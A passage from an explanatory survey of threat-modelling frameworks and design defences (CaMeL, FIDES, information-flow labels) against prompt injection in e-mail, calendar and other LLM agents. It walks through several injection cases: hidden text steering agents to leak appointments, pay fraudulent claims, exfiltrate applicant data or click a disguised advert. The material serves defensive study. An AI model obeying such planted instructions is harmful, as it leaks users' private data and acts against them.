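| Stranger's e-mail | read_email → list_events → image in the reply | The user's screen requests an address that contains the appointments | The display loads images only from listed hosts |
| E-mail from someone posing as Priya | read_email → update_event | The meeting moves to a time Priya never proposed | The harness accepts new times only from a verified guest |
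| Stranger's e-mail | read_email → repeated send_email | The user's contacts receive fraudulent messages in her name | Recipient approval and an hourly limit |
| Stranger's e-mail | read_email → update_event, then list_events in a later session | The instruction survives in the event's notes | The harness stores the text's origin with the notes |
| Stranger's e-mail | read_email → a long series of calls | The mail service blocks the account for overuse | The harness stops a run after a fixed number of calls |

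Schneider recommends attacking the controls on paper before building them. The analyst asks what happens if each control fails, if someone configures it wrongly, or if the attacker knows about it. Several controls in the table depend on the user's approval, so a user who clicks "yes" without reading would undo all of them at once. The developer could ask for approval less often by taking Priya's address from the user's contacts and asking only about other recipients.

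She could also reserve approval for actions that are hard to reverse. Microsoft advises constraining high-impact or irreversible actions through validation, policy checks or human approval. Nobody can recall the appointments once a stranger has them. But the user can move a meeting back if she notices the change before Friday, so a clear notice with an undo button may be enough for that action.

### Checking the diagram against the lethal trifecta

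*The lethal trifecta for AI agents* (Willison, 2025) offers a quick check for data theft. An agent is vulnerable if it has access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to communicate externally. The assistant has all three. Removing any one of them blocks the attack, so a designer doesn't need to predict the attacker's wording or estimate how often the model will resist.

Willison argues that the route for sending data out is generally the easiest of the three to remove. A designer still has to find every such route. He points out that any tool able to make a web request can carry stolen data, and so can a link the user clicks. Removing send_email from the assistant would still let data leave through the invitations and images.

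The check covers only data theft. Blue41, a company that sells runtime monitoring for agents, describes an insurer's agent that reads claims and can approve payments. A claimant uses hidden text in a document to tell the agent that the claim is verified and that it should pay €4,800 to a given account. The insurer loses money even though no confidential information leaks. In another version, the hidden text makes the agent look up every past claim one at a time until the lookup service blocks the agent, and honest claimants have to wait.

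The fifth row of the assistant's table is a harm of the first type. Even if the developer closed every exit for data, someone posing as Priya could still have the meeting moved. Willison didn't set out to cover this kind of harm, so passing his check doesn't show that an agent is safe in general.

### Meta's Rule of Two

Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) extends the trifecta to cover harmful actions. It allows an agent to have at most two of these properties in one session without supervision:

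- A: it can process untrustworthy inputs.
- B: it can access sensitive systems or private data.
- C: it can change state or communicate externally.

Meta's example is an e-mail agent much like the assistant. Without property A, it would process messages only from trustworthy senders, such as close friends. Without B, it would work in an environment with nothing sensitive, such as a test mailbox. To restrict C, it could send new messages only to trusted recipients or only after a person had checked the draft. An agent that needs all three properties must have human approval or another reliable check.

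The third arrangement suits the assistant best. If it ignored strangers, it would miss much of its user's mail, and hostile text could still reach it when trusted senders quoted it. Under Meta's rule, moving a meeting also counts as changing state, so the developer would have to control update_event as well as send_email. The rule would also cover the insurance fraud, because a payment system is sensitive and making a payment changes its state.

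Willison objected in *New prompt injection papers* (2025) that an agent with only A and C can still do harm. Suppose an agent manages a village hall's bookings on a public calendar. It reads requests from anyone (A) and can change the calendar (C), but has no access to private data. A hostile request could make it cancel every booking. Meta could reply that the calendar is a sensitive system, which would give the agent property B as well. But if anything worth protecting from changes counts as sensitive, every agent that can do harm by changing something has B. The rule would then require supervision whenever an agent acts on untrusted text, and counting the properties would be redundant.

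Counting by session can also miss untrusted text saved in an earlier session. Suppose the assistant reads a stranger's e-mail on Monday and copies part of it into a calendar event's notes. On Tuesday it starts with a clean context, reads only the calendar and sends an e-mail. If the analyst treats the notes as the user's own words, Tuesday's session appears to have only B and C, but the labels from step 4 show that it also has A.

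Meta allows an agent to change configuration during a session. For example, it could browse the web first, then lose the ability to communicate before gaining access to internal systems. Meta warns that a design can satisfy the rule and still fail, such as when a user confirms a warning without reading it.

### What the published frameworks make an analyst do

Security organisations have published several frameworks for agents, many of which add lists of threats to consider. They differ mainly in the work they ask of the analyst:

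| Method | What the analyst does | What she has at the end |
|---|---|---|
| MAESTRO | Goes through seven layers of the agent's technology | Threats grouped by layer |
| OWASP Top 10 for Agentic Applications | Compares the system with ten named risks | The risks that apply, with suggested mitigations |
| MITRE ATLAS | Looks up known techniques for attacking AI systems | A description of possible attacks in standard terms |
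| Attack tree | Works backwards from one harm | The conditions an attacker needs and where to break them |
| Threat snapshot | Freezes the agent at one call to the model | A repeatable test with a score |

Ken Huang introduced MAESTRO (Multi-Agent Environment, Security, Threat, Risk and Outcome), which the Cloud Security Alliance publishes. Its layers are foundation models, data operations, agent frameworks, deployment and infrastructure, evaluation and observability, security and compliance, and the agent ecosystem. Going through them would remind the assistant's developer to consider two threats missing from the table above, a compromised software library and a monitoring log that stores private mail.

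MAESTRO's layers are less helpful for classifying threats. Bishop Fox's example, an agent that books flights, first puts excessive permissions under security and compliance (layer 6), but later puts write access to an approval database under deployment and infrastructure (layer 4). Either label would lead to the same fix. The calendar leak involves several layers, and an analyst who filled in each one separately could repeat the mistake of a component-by-component STRIDE review.

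In one of Bishop Fox's booking examples, an airline lowers its ticket price and raises its fees, so that the agent picks a more expensive trip as the "cheapest flight". The consultancy places this under adversarial AI, but the airline only has to publish prices, with no hostile instructions. An analyst is more likely to find this threat by asking who benefits from the agent's choice than by looking for prompt injection.

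In December 2025, OWASP, a non-profit that publishes software security guidance, released its list of ten agentic risks: goal hijack, tool misuse, identity and privilege abuse, supply-chain vulnerabilities, unexpected code execution, memory and context poisoning, insecure communication between agents, cascading failures, exploitation of human trust, and rogue agents. At least the first three apply to the calendar leak, since the stranger redirected the model, had it misuse send_email and benefited from the user's permissions. The analyst has to find a route herself before she can use the list to name it and look up mitigations.

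MITRE, a US non-profit research organisation, modelled ATLAS on ATT&CK, its catalogue of how intruders attack ordinary computer systems. Shostack (2026), in *PHANTOM-B*, rates ATLAS as very detailed but hard to learn and use, and notes that most of its tactics overlap with ATT&CK's. He rates OWASP's list for language-model applications as easy to learn but repetitive. These are one consultant's judgements, and the paper introduces his own competing method, which he rates as requiring the least effort of those compared. His colleague Dandy reports similar complaints from clients, who spent time on catalogues and found threats they already knew about or could do nothing about.

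### Testing one moment at a time

A threat model identifies what could happen, but a developer may also want to know how likely a particular model is to do what an attacker intends. *Breaking Agent Backbones* (Bazinska, Mathys and colleagues, 2025) introduced threat snapshots to measure this without building a whole agent for each test.

One way to draw a threat model for an agent is to treat the language model as a function m that takes the context C at step t and returns an output, O = m(C). The model keeps nothing between calls, so everything that can influence its next output is in that context. A threat snapshot records the agent's purpose and current state, the full context, the place where an attacker can insert text, and a rule that scores the output from 0 to 1 by how well it achieves the attacker's goal.

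A developer could freeze the assistant's run just after read_email returned the stranger's message, and score it 1 if the model next asked for the whole week's events. A second snapshot would start with those events already in the context and test whether the model sent them to the stranger. If, to use invented figures, the first step succeeded in 30% of runs and the second succeeded in half of those, the whole attack would succeed 15% of the time. Multiplying the rates is valid only if the second snapshot uses contexts like those the first step produces. Bazinska and colleagues describe chaining snapshots this way, but their benchmark uses single steps.

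The benchmark has 30 snapshots, made up of ten applications in three versions each. The first version is basic, with few security instructions. The second has a more elaborate system prompt and, where relevant, more harmless data in the context. The third is the basic version with a second call to the same model to judge the exchange. To obtain realistic attacks, the researchers turned the snapshots into a public game and collected 194,331 unique attacks, from which they built the benchmark. They ran each of the benchmark's attacks several times because a model's answers vary.

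Across 34 models, those with stronger reasoning were more secure, but larger models were not generally more secure than smaller ones. A developer therefore shouldn't assume that the biggest model will resist attacks best. The comparison used the same attacks on every model, whereas a real attacker could tailor them to the target. It also deliberately left out the harness. If the harness blocks every way to send data out, the model can't leak the calendar, whatever its score. Otherwise, even a high-scoring model can leak it by following one hostile e-mail.

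The framework can also help an analyst find threats. Its attacks come either directly from the user or indirectly through text the model reads, and each has one of six goals: stealing data, inserting content, manipulating decisions, denying service, compromising systems or tools, and bypassing content policies. The analyst can go through the twelve combinations and write a snapshot for each that applies. Considering indirect attacks that manipulate decisions would lead her to the false message from Priya, which she would miss if she looked only for theft.

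### Guidance and standards

A company that buys an agent may want evidence that the developer has dealt with the threats. AIUC-1, a standard from the Artificial Intelligence Underwriting Company, has about fifty requirements for agents. Schneider explains that independent auditors issue certificates valid for one year and repeat some tests every quarter. To show that an agent can't take unauthorised actions, for example, a developer has to produce the configuration that lists the services the agent can reach.

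In May 2026 OWASP published a crosswalk that links each of its ten agentic risks to requirements in the AIUC-1 standard. Two requirements, on preventing unauthorised actions and restricting unsafe tool calls, are primary controls for six of the ten risks. OWASP cautions that the crosswalk "identifies relevance, not sufficiency". OWASP also found eight gaps where the standard lacked a suitable requirement. Schneider advises developers who add a control to fill such a gap to record the attack path that justifies it, so that nobody later removes the control because no auditor asks for it.

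The AIUC-1 standard changes every quarter, and Schneider found that the crosswalk still cited a retired requirement. A developer who relied on the crosswalk alone could prepare evidence for a rule that no longer exists.

In August 2025 the US National Institute of Standards and Technology (NIST) also proposed adapting existing controls. Its control overlays for AI would select and adjust entries from its general catalogue of security controls for particular uses. One overlay would cover single agents, and another would cover systems of several agents.

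Guidance from software companies focuses more on what happens after deployment. OpenAI tells security teams to check whom an agent is acting for and whether its task stays within permitted bounds. Microsoft suggests judging a threat-modelling programme partly by whether monitoring reveals misuse before users complain. For the assistant, this would mean logging the context behind each call to send_email, because the outgoing message alone wouldn't show that a stranger had asked for it.

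### Whether STRIDE is enough

Shostack argues that agents don't need a new type of data-flow diagram or a replacement for STRIDE. He would use STRIDE on the whole system and add eight prompts to help people think of threats to the parts that call a language model: prompt injection, hallucination, anthropomorphisation, non-explainability, training issues, over-reliance, missing security engineering and biases. He warns that a threat may not fit neatly under any one of them.

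Bishop Fox writes that "AI doesn't break STRIDE". In the simplest version of its booking agent, the model only fetches approved vendors and employee profiles from an internal database. Replacing the model with an ordinary program would barely change the threats, so STRIDE works as usual. Bishop Fox turns to MAESTRO once the agent can contact outside vendors and use the company's approval process.

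Some evidence also suggests that the six categories are broad enough. *Talk is (Not) Cheap* (Iyer, Jamshidi and colleagues, 2026) builds a taxonomy of attacks on language models from 932 security studies and organises it in a grid of four targets and six techniques based on STRIDE. Of its 507 entries, 401 came from the studies and 106 from threat modelling. However, putting a known attack in a category is easier than using the category to discover a new one.

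Schneider replies that analysts miss the attack when they apply STRIDE to each component separately, but find it when they apply it to the whole attack path. The categories fit the stranger's route through the assistant well. The stranger's text passes for the user's instructions (spoofing), gains her permissions (elevation of privilege) and makes the assistant send out her appointments (information disclosure), while the mail log lists her as the sender (repudiation).

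The frameworks disagree less than their titles suggest. Shostack supplements STRIDE, and Schneider says that his method adds to traditional threat modelling without replacing it. STRIDE's categories cover the harm, as its defenders say, but an analyst has to connect a message in the mailbox to a recipient in send_email before she can apply them to the route, and the categories don't include instructions for doing that. An analyst who already follows data across the whole system may need little beyond STRIDE and the rule that model output is untrusted, but one who fills in a table for each component needs the extra steps.

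The evidence offered for particular frameworks doesn't show which one helps analysts most. In *Why PHANTOM-B?*, Shostack says his firm developed and validated the method with very large cloud companies and major financial institutions, and that teams can apply it in under an hour. He gives no figures for the threats teams found using it.

*Securing Agentic AI* (Zambare, Thanikella and Liu, 2025) applies MAESTRO to a prototype agent that monitors a network, then demonstrates two of the threats. Replaying network traffic overloaded the agent and delayed its updates, and altering its log of past events corrupted its memory. The demonstrations confirm that the threats were real, but STRIDE already covers both, as denial of service and tampering.

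*STRIDE-AI* (2026), which adapts STRIDE to generative AI, reports that the attack success rate against one chatbot fell from 80% to 15%. That drop measures the effect of the defences added after the analysis, and an analyst using a different method might have chosen the same ones.

A direct test would be to give several groups of analysts the same agent and the same amount of time, assign each group a method, and compare their findings with attacks that a separate team had carried out successfully. The comparison should also include the number of threats that nobody could act on, since Dandy's clients were already getting too many of those.

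## Designs that limit what a misled model can do

Engineers who can't stop a stranger's e-mail from misleading the model can still limit what the misled model can do. Several designs do this with ordinary code and give formal guarantees, which hold whatever the model outputs as long as certain assumptions about the rest of the system are true.

David C quotes an informal version of the idea from an exchange on X between Willison and Baibhav Bista. When a model processes information from a party, its privileges should drop to that party's. A stranger can't read the user's calendar or send mail in her name, so an assistant that has just read the stranger's e-mail shouldn't be able to either.

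Information-flow control governs what should happen after the model has read text from several parties, and who may receive what it then writes. It labels data by secrecy and trustworthiness, and blocks flows that break a rule about the labels.

### Two labels and how they combine

Costa, Köpf and colleagues (2025), in *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, attach both labels to everything an agent processes. The trust label is T (trusted) or U (untrusted). In the version of the secrecy label that suits e-mail best, the label is the set of people who may read the data. When a new value draws on two older ones, x and y, its labels are:

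```
trust(x, y)   = T if x and y are both T, otherwise U
readers(x, y) = readers(x) ∩ readers(y)
```

The trust rule is the threat model's lowest-rank rule with only two ranks. Combining documents can remove permitted readers but can't add any. If Ann and Ben may read one document, and Ben and Carl another, only Ben may read a summary of both.

For the e-mail and calendar assistant, the labels might be:

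| Item | Trust | Who may read it |
|---|---|---|
| The user's request | T | Anyone |
| Priya's e-mail | U | The user and Priya |
| The stranger's e-mail | U | The user and the stranger |
| Thursday's meeting, which the user created | T | The user and Priya |
| A medical appointment | T | The user |

The harness checks two rules before a tool call. Kolluri, Sharma and colleagues (2026), in *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy*, call them "trusted action" and "permitted flow". The trusted-action rule allows a call with real consequences only if the model chose it in a trusted context. The permitted-flow rule allows data to leave only if every recipient may read it.

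After read_email returns Priya's message and the stranger's, the context is untrusted, and its readers are {user, Priya} ∩ {user, stranger} = {user}. Adding the calendar entries changes neither label. If the model tries to send the medical appointment to the stranger, the call breaks both rules, because the model chose it after reading untrusted text and the stranger isn't among the readers.

The harmless confirmation to Priya also breaks both rules, because the model wrote it in the same context and nobody can precisely trace which inputs shaped a model's output. An assistant with only these labels added would be secure but couldn't finish the job. To let the confirmation through, a designer has to keep the stranger's text away from the model that chooses the calls.

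### One model to plan and another to read

In *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, Willison (2023) proposed splitting the work between two models. A privileged model takes the user's request and can call tools, but never reads untrusted text. A quarantined model reads untrusted text but has no tools. An ordinary program, the controller, runs the calls and stores the results.

Suppose the user asks for a summary of her latest e-mail. The privileged model sends the controller a command to fetch it. The controller stores the message under a name such as $VAR1 and returns only the name. The privileged model then requests a summary of $VAR1, so the controller passes the message to the quarantined model and stores the output as $VAR2. Finally, the privileged model sends a command to show $VAR2 to the user. A hostile e-mail can corrupt the summary, but the privileged model, which has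 access to the tools, never receives the text of the e-mail or the summary.

Willison allowed one exception. The controller may pass on an answer from the quarantined model if it can verify that the answer belongs to a fixed set of categories.

The pattern guarantees that untrusted text can't choose a tool, as long as the controller never passes such text to the model that does the choosing and the user doesn't paste any into her own request. Willison called his solution "pretty bad" because it would be complicated to build and unpleasant to use. He proposed it without reporting any measurements.

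Two years later, researchers at Google and ETH Zurich found a flaw in it, which Willison (2025) accepted in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks*. In their example, a user asks an assistant to send Bob a document, and Bob's address is in some meeting notes. The privileged model correctly plans to find the address and send the document. But the quarantined model has to read the notes to find the address, and hostile text there can make it return the attacker's address instead, so the assistant follows the correct plan but sends the document to the attacker.

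### CaMeL writes the program before it reads the data

CaMeL, which Debenedetti and colleagues presented in the same work, adds a record of where each value came from. The privileged model sees only the user's request and descriptions of the tools, and turns the request into a complete program in a restricted form of Python. For the request to move Thursday's meeting, it might write the following, where PRIYA is an address from the user's contacts:

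```
mail    = read_email(sender=PRIYA)
time    = quarantined_model("Find the proposed time", mail, output=datetime)
events  = list_events(day="Thursday")
meeting = quarantined_model("Find the meeting with Priya", events, output=event_id)
update_event(meeting, start=time)
send_email(to=PRIYA, subject="Thursday's meeting", body=time)
```

A custom interpreter then runs the program. Data from tools may affect which of the program's existing branches runs, but can't add a step. Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) call this guarantee control-flow integrity in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*. This program contains no call that sends anything to the stranger, and the stranger's e-mail can't add one, however persuasive it is.

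The interpreter also attaches what CaMeL calls capabilities to every value. According to *CaMeLoT* (2026), these record the value's sources and who may read it. Before each tool call, the interpreter runs a policy, a short Python function that checks these capabilities. A policy for update_event could accept a new time only if all its sources are guests at the meeting. This would stop an attacker who poses as Priya from another address, which no check on the call's format would catch.

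If the program fetched the twenty newest messages instead of Priya's, all twenty would be among the new time's sources, and the policy would reject it even if the quarantined model had found the right one.

CaMeL's guarantee depends on a trustworthy request, a sound privileged model, tools that work as described, and an interpreter that tracks values correctly. Protection against false arguments also depends on having the right policies. Because the interpreter checks policies while the program runs, it could move the meeting and then block the message to Priya. *CaMeLoT* extends CaMeL with checks on the plan before it runs.

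### Capabilities and the confused deputy

Hardy's capabilities, his remedy for the confused deputy, are slightly different because each one is itself the permission to use something. In the assistant, send_email could require a recipient object that the harness creates for Priya only when the user names her. The assistant would then lack a general permission to send mail, which a stranger could otherwise exploit. The object wouldn't restrict the message's contents, but CaMeL's list of readers can.

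The two meanings are related. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026) point out in *The LLMbda Calculus* that a system of labels can treat a capability as a token that carries a trusted label and that a tool requires before it acts.

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (2026) describes TACIT, a system that checks code instead of data. The model writes programs in Scala 3, and the compiler checks them before they run. A function that processes secret data receives no capability to print, write files or use the network, so it cannot leak the data. TACIT allows recursive and user-defined functions, which CaMeL bans to keep its tracking manageable.

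### FIDES plans one step at a time

CaMeL's privileged model has to plan for every case before it reads any data. In FIDES, which Costa and colleagues built at Microsoft, the planning model chooses one step at a time and sees as much of the data as is safe. When a tool returns a result, FIDES compares each field's label with the context's label. It shows the model the fields that wouldn't lower the context's trust and replaces the others with variables. In the assistant's mailbox, the planner might see each message's arrival time and verified sender address, but a variable in place of the text.

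The planner can pass a variable to a tool or have a quarantined model process it. It can also inspect the variable, but this puts the contents in its context, which makes the context untrusted and may rule out later calls.

Suppose the user asks the assistant to check her three latest e-mails for a meeting request and, if there is one, add it to her calendar. Costa and colleagues work through this task in five steps:

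1. The planner fetches the e-mails, and FIDES stores their text in variables.
2. The quarantined model answers yes or no to the question of whether there is a request.
3. The planner inspects that answer.
4. If it is yes, the quarantined model extracts the details into another variable.
5. The planner passes the variable to the calendar.

The yes-or-no answer is untrusted and makes the context untrusted too. But FIDES also records the answer's type, so a policy can accept a single bit where it would reject free text. A stranger could cause an unwanted calendar entry but couldn't give the planner new instructions. The developer would have to limit the number of such answers, because many single bits can carry a long message, just as 80 free-or-busy replies revealed a week's calendar.

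FIDES guarantees a form of confidentiality called explicit secrecy, which stops secret data from being copied, directly or through other values, into anything an attacker can observe. It doesn't cover what someone can infer from the agent's choice of actions. If the assistant writes to Priya only when Friday is free, she learns something about Friday from whether a message arrives. Costa and colleagues accept this gap because closing it would mean banning almost all outside actions once the agent had read a secret. They also assume that the user, the models and the tool descriptions are trustworthy.

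In tests with a fixed set of attacks, 152 succeeded against an ordinary agent. FIDES reduced this to 21 without policy checks and to none with them, after the researchers removed cases that the benchmark misjudged. The 21 successes show that hiding text in variables isn't enough if the planner is free to open them.

### Six patterns and what each gives up

Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues (2025), in *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections*, doubt that general-purpose agents can be reliably secure with current models. They recommend building agents for narrower jobs, on the principle that once an agent has taken in untrusted text, that text must be unable to trigger any consequential action. They describe six ways to do this:

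| Pattern | How it works | What the assistant would lose |
|---|---|---|
| Action selector | The model picks from a fixed list of actions and never sees their results | It couldn't use the time Priya proposed |
| Plan, then execute | The model fixes its list of calls before reading any data | It couldn't add a step because of something in an e-mail |
| Map-reduce | A separate model reads each document and returns something simple, such as yes or no | It couldn't freely combine details from several e-mails |
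| Dual model | A privileged model plans, and a quarantined model reads | The planner couldn't react to what an e-mail says |
| Code, then execute | The model writes a program first, as in CaMeL | The program would have to anticipate every case |
| Context minimisation | The system removes the user's prompt before the model writes its reply | The reply couldn't take account of the user's wording |

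Context minimisation guards against hostile text in the user's own prompt, so it suits a public chatbot whose users may try to persuade it to give them a discount. It wouldn't help against the stranger, whose text isn't in the user's prompt.

"Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections" includes an e-mail and calendar assistant among its ten case studies. The paper considers it very unlikely that the assistant's choice and order of actions would need to depend on untrusted data, so planning in advance would have little downside for most uses. The plan would still need some flexibility. For example, if a user asks the assistant to tell her regular collaborators about her holiday, it has to make the plan before it knows how many people to write to.

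Costa and colleagues offer some support for this. They sorted the 97 tasks in AgentDojo, a benchmark of simulated office, travel, banking and Slack work, by whether the right steps depend on what the agent reads. The steps depended on it in only 5% of the office tasks, but in more than 40% of the banking and Slack tasks. Researchers invented these tasks, so the share in a real mailbox may differ.

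### The cost in completed tasks

The same benchmark shows what the guarantees cost. Costa and colleagues measured the percentage of tasks that agents running on GPT-4o, an older OpenAI model, completed when nobody was attacking:

| | Office | Travel | Banking | Slack |
|---|---:|---:|---:|---:|
| Ordinary agent, no checks | 75.0 | 70.0 | 98.8 | 93.3 |
| Ordinary agent with labels and checks | 37.0 | 73.0 | 37.5 | 20.0 |
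| FIDES with checks | 59.0 | 41.0 | 52.5 | 47.6 |

The average completion rate, with each column weighted equally, fell from 84% for the ordinary agent to 50% for FIDES. Some of this loss is likely to shrink as models improve. GPT-4o often confused variable names, and FIDES completed 68% of the travel tasks with o1, a stronger model, compared with 41% with GPT-4o. Other failures were intentional, because several banking tasks ask the agent to read a file and do what it says, which the trusted-action rule prevents.

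CaMeL's policies can reduce task completion just as much. Garby and colleagues ran CaMeL three times on each of 16 banking tasks. With policies on, it completed 18 of 48 runs with each of the two models they tried, about half as many as with policies off. It also blocked every attack with policies on, while a few succeeded with policies off.

Planning in advance provides much of the protection by itself. In 97 of the 144 pairings of a banking task with an attack, the attack required a tool call or file that would never appear in a plan for the user's task. Policies matter for the other 47, in which the attacker could misuse a step already in the plan. A high overall security score can therefore be a poor measure of how well a system's policies work.

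Kolluri and colleagues argue that the usual comparison is unfair because the secure agent never asks for help, while the unprotected agent would in practice need a person to approve its actions. GitHub Copilot Chat in Visual Studio Code, for example, reads freely but asks before making other tool calls. When the researchers counted only tasks completed without any approval, an ordinary agent on the model o3-mini scored 24.3%, because it had to ask before every consequential action, and FIDES scored 50.1%. Flow control therefore benefits a company that would otherwise approve every action, but a company that would otherwise let the agent act unchecked will get fewer tasks completed.

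These designs also use extra tokens and time. Kolluri and colleagues acknowledge that flow-control defences use more tokens than filters or training, but the number of turns need not grow much. On WASP, a benchmark of tasks on simulated websites, their GPT-4o agent took 6.1 turns per GitLab task, compared with 5.5 for an unprotected agent. On Reddit tasks, their agent took 8.5 turns and the unprotected agent took 8.6. Turns are only a rough guide to time and money, because some take much longer than others.

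### When agents call other agents

Suppose a developer divides the assistant into a coordinator, a mail reader and a mail sender, and protects each with CaMeL. The coordinator's program gets a summary from the reader, pastes it into an instruction, and tells the sender to forward it to Priya. The coordinator's planner never reads the summary, but the sender's planner does, because the sender treats the whole instruction as a request from its user. A hostile sentence in the summary can then lead that planner to add a step to the sender's program.

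Peters-Gill and colleagues demonstrated this with a database of job applicants. They asked three agents running on GPT-5.2 to send a summary to a colleague on Slack. An instruction hidden in the database made the last agent also e-mail the data to an outside address, even though every agent had CaMeL's control-flow protection. The researchers had turned off flow policies, and a good policy on outgoing mail might have stopped the leak. Even so, the agents had lost the guarantee that untrusted text can't add a step. Under mild assumptions, any hierarchy of such agents loses this guarantee if it has a tool that returns untrusted data.

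The paper's remedy, multi-CaMeL, sends instructions and data between agents through separate channels, so that the receiving planner reads only the instructions. On the paper's benchmark, attacks succeeded 12.9% of the time without CaMeL, 0.2% with CaMeL in each agent and 0.0% with multi-CaMeL. The difference between the last two is small, but the demonstration shows that a suitably placed instruction can get past CaMeL in each agent. Multi-CaMeL completed fewer tasks, though the loss was modest with the strongest models.

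### When the agent works on a screen

*CaMeLs Can Use Computers Too* (Foerster, Blanchard and colleagues, 2026) adapted CaMeL to agents that operate a computer by looking at the screen and clicking. These agents normally decide each click after seeing the result of the last one. The researchers instead had the planner write a program with a branch for every situation it could foresee, such as a cookie banner that might appear. The programs averaged about 41 tool calls, compared with 5 for CaMeL's programs on AgentDojo, and roughly half the steps were fallbacks that a given run never used. The agents kept up to 57% of the performance of leading models on a benchmark of computer tasks.

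An attacker can't add a step to such a program but can still influence which branch runs. Foerster and colleagues call this branch steering. In one attack, they disguised an advertisement as a cookie banner. The program had a step for dismissing cookie banners, so the agent clicked the advertisement and opened the attacker's website.

Policies are little help when a model operates a computer by clicking on the screen. A policy can check the recipient of a send_email call, but a click has only coordinates, and the same click could close a banner or delete a file. The researchers instead tested cross-checks between the screenshot and the page's code, and between two models. These checks make an attack harder but don't rule it out, and the researchers found ways to attack both kinds.

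### Leaks that labels miss

Labels protect data only where the software tracks them. Garby and colleagues found gaps in CaMeL's tracking, including one that researchers first described in the 1970s. Adapted to the assistant, it looks like this:

```
free = True
busy = True
if friday_has_appointment: free = False
if free: busy = False
if busy: send_email(...)
```

If the user has an appointment on Friday, the third line changes `free`, and CaMeL marks that variable as secret. The fourth line then does nothing, so `busy` is never marked. The message goes out, and because none is sent when Friday is clear, its arrival reveals the appointment. CaMeL missed the leak because it marked only the variables that a run changed, and here `busy` revealed the appointment by staying unchanged.

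A stranger can't write this code into CaMeL's plan, so an attack would depend on the privileged model producing something similar. The other gap is in the loop that restarts CaMeL after a failed attempt. Whether a policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit about a secret, and repeated attempts could reveal the rest because the loop is outside CaMeL's tracking.

Garby and colleagues built a small programming language in which every operation carries labels forward, and used proof-checking software to verify that it guarantees noninterference. This means that secret inputs can't affect what an outsider sees, and untrusted inputs can't affect trusted results, except through whether the program finishes. The guarantee covers programs that the model writes during a run. The FIDES guarantee, by contrast, covers copied data but not inferences from the agent's choices. On the banking tasks, Garby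 and colleagues' agent completed about twice as many runs as CaMeL did with its policies on.

The proof can't show that the labels are right. If the assistant's developer labels every calendar entry as trusted, a stranger's invitation is trusted too. Willison's main worry about CaMeL was that people have to write and maintain its policies, which he finds hard even as a specialist.

Labels that follow copied data can also miss subtler influence. *From Agent Traces to Trust* (2026), a survey, concludes that "unsafe behavior can arise from influence, not content alone". *Ghost in the Agent* presents NeuroTaint, which looks for untrusted text that was reworded, affected a decision or returned from memory in a later session. In 400 test scenarios, it traced such influence substantially better than a version of FIDES. However, NeuroTaint examines runs offline, so it can help an investigator but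 cannot block a call.

### False content in a permitted flow

Even a perfect tracking system would not prevent all harm. Suppose the user asks the assistant to summarise three e-mails for a colleague. An instruction hidden in one e-mail can make the quarantined model return an empty summary. The assistant then makes the planned calls and sends the colleague a useless message.

Beurer-Kellner and colleagues describe a worse case, in which the user asks for a reply to a stranger's e-mail based on the user's recent mail. Hidden text in the stranger's message could make the model add private information to the reply, encoded in characters that don't appear on the screen. Because the user wanted to reply to the stranger, only a restriction on the reply's contents could stop the leak. If the harness applied the permitted-flow rule strictly, the rule would stop the leak, but it would also block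 the reply the user asked for, because that reply draws on other people's e-mails.

Attacks on the agent that Garby and colleagues built succeeded in only two of 1,296 runs. In both, the user had asked the agent to read a file and make the payment described there, and the attacker had replaced the file with a different payment request. The agent followed the user's instruction and made the substituted payment. Garby and colleagues note that CaMeL's developers had excluded the same case from their threat model. Labels can show that the file is untrusted, but not whether the payment request in it is genuine.

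### When the next step depends on untrusted text

Some requests require the agent to follow someone else's instructions. For example, a user may forward an e-mail from her manager listing ten small jobs and ask the assistant to do them. A plan written before the assistant reads the e-mail cannot list the jobs, and a design that withdraws permissions once the assistant reads untrusted text would stop it from doing them.

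A capable planner may work around this in a way that defeats the design. Garby and colleagues gave CaMeL, with its policies off, a task to read a file and follow its instructions precisely. The privileged model couldn't see the instructions, so it wrote a program with a branch for each tool, and the file's contents determined which one ran. The attacks succeeded in two trials even though the program followed its own control flow, so control-flow integrity gives little protection if the plan allows every action.

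The designer can refuse such requests, restrict them to a few fixed actions, or ask the user.

### Human approval as an exception

In flow control, approval is an exception to a rule. The user can either permit a single call despite its labels or change a label. Relabelling data from untrusted to trusted is called endorsement, and relabelling it so that more people can read it is called declassification.

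Prudentia, an agent that Kolluri and colleagues built on FIDES, offers both approval and endorsement. If the user endorses the manager's e-mail once, the agent can do all ten jobs without asking her to approve each one. The researchers left out declassification because whether to share a secret usually depends on who is asking and why, and they prefer that the user judge each call.

Endorsement takes less effort than approving each call, but a mistake can do more harm. If the e-mail contains an eleventh instruction hidden in white text, endorsing the e-mail gives that instruction the user's authority too, whereas mistakenly approving one call affects only that call.

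Prudentia also gives its planner the labels and rules, so it can look for a way to do the task that needs no exception. With the model o4-mini, this roughly halved interventions across all completed tasks, from 36.8 with FIDES to 19.2, while the share of tasks completed fell slightly, from 75.7% to 73.2%. On WASP, where the tasks were posting comments and upvoting posts, Prudentia needed no approvals.

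Reducing the number of approval requests matters because people may stop reading them. Willison predicted in 2023 that users would learn to click "OK" as fast as possible, so approval would fail as a security measure. Two years later he pointed out that Troy Hunt, a security researcher, had recently fallen for a phishing message while tired. Kolluri and colleagues cite research from 2011 and 2016 on people growing numb to security prompts. But their own experiments assume a user who rejects every harmful call, so they measure interruptions and don't show how many attacks a tired user would approve. Approval fatigue in agents is plausible, but the case for it in these works rests on experience with other kinds of warning.

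Beurer-Kellner and colleagues note that even a vigilant user could miss information hidden in invisible characters, and that checking an e-mail is much harder through a voice assistant than on a screen. Skipping approval for e-mails to colleagues would reduce the user's burden, but a hijacked assistant could then ask a co-worker to ignore a security alert.

Kolluri and colleagues suggest using the labels to make each request more informative. For the leaked calendar, the harness could show the user that the message contains appointments only she may read, and that the recipient's address came from a stranger's e-mail. She would have a much better chance of catching the attack than if she saw only a prompt to send a message called "Next week".

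## Experiments on how often attacks get past defences

CaMeL and FIDES limit what a misled model can do, but agents that use them complete fewer tasks. A developer who can't accept that loss can try to make the model harder to mislead, or put a detector in front of it. Researchers test these defences on simulated agents. Their results depend heavily on whether the attacker may revise a failed attack, and on whether they calculate the success rate per attempt or per scenario.

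### How a test is built

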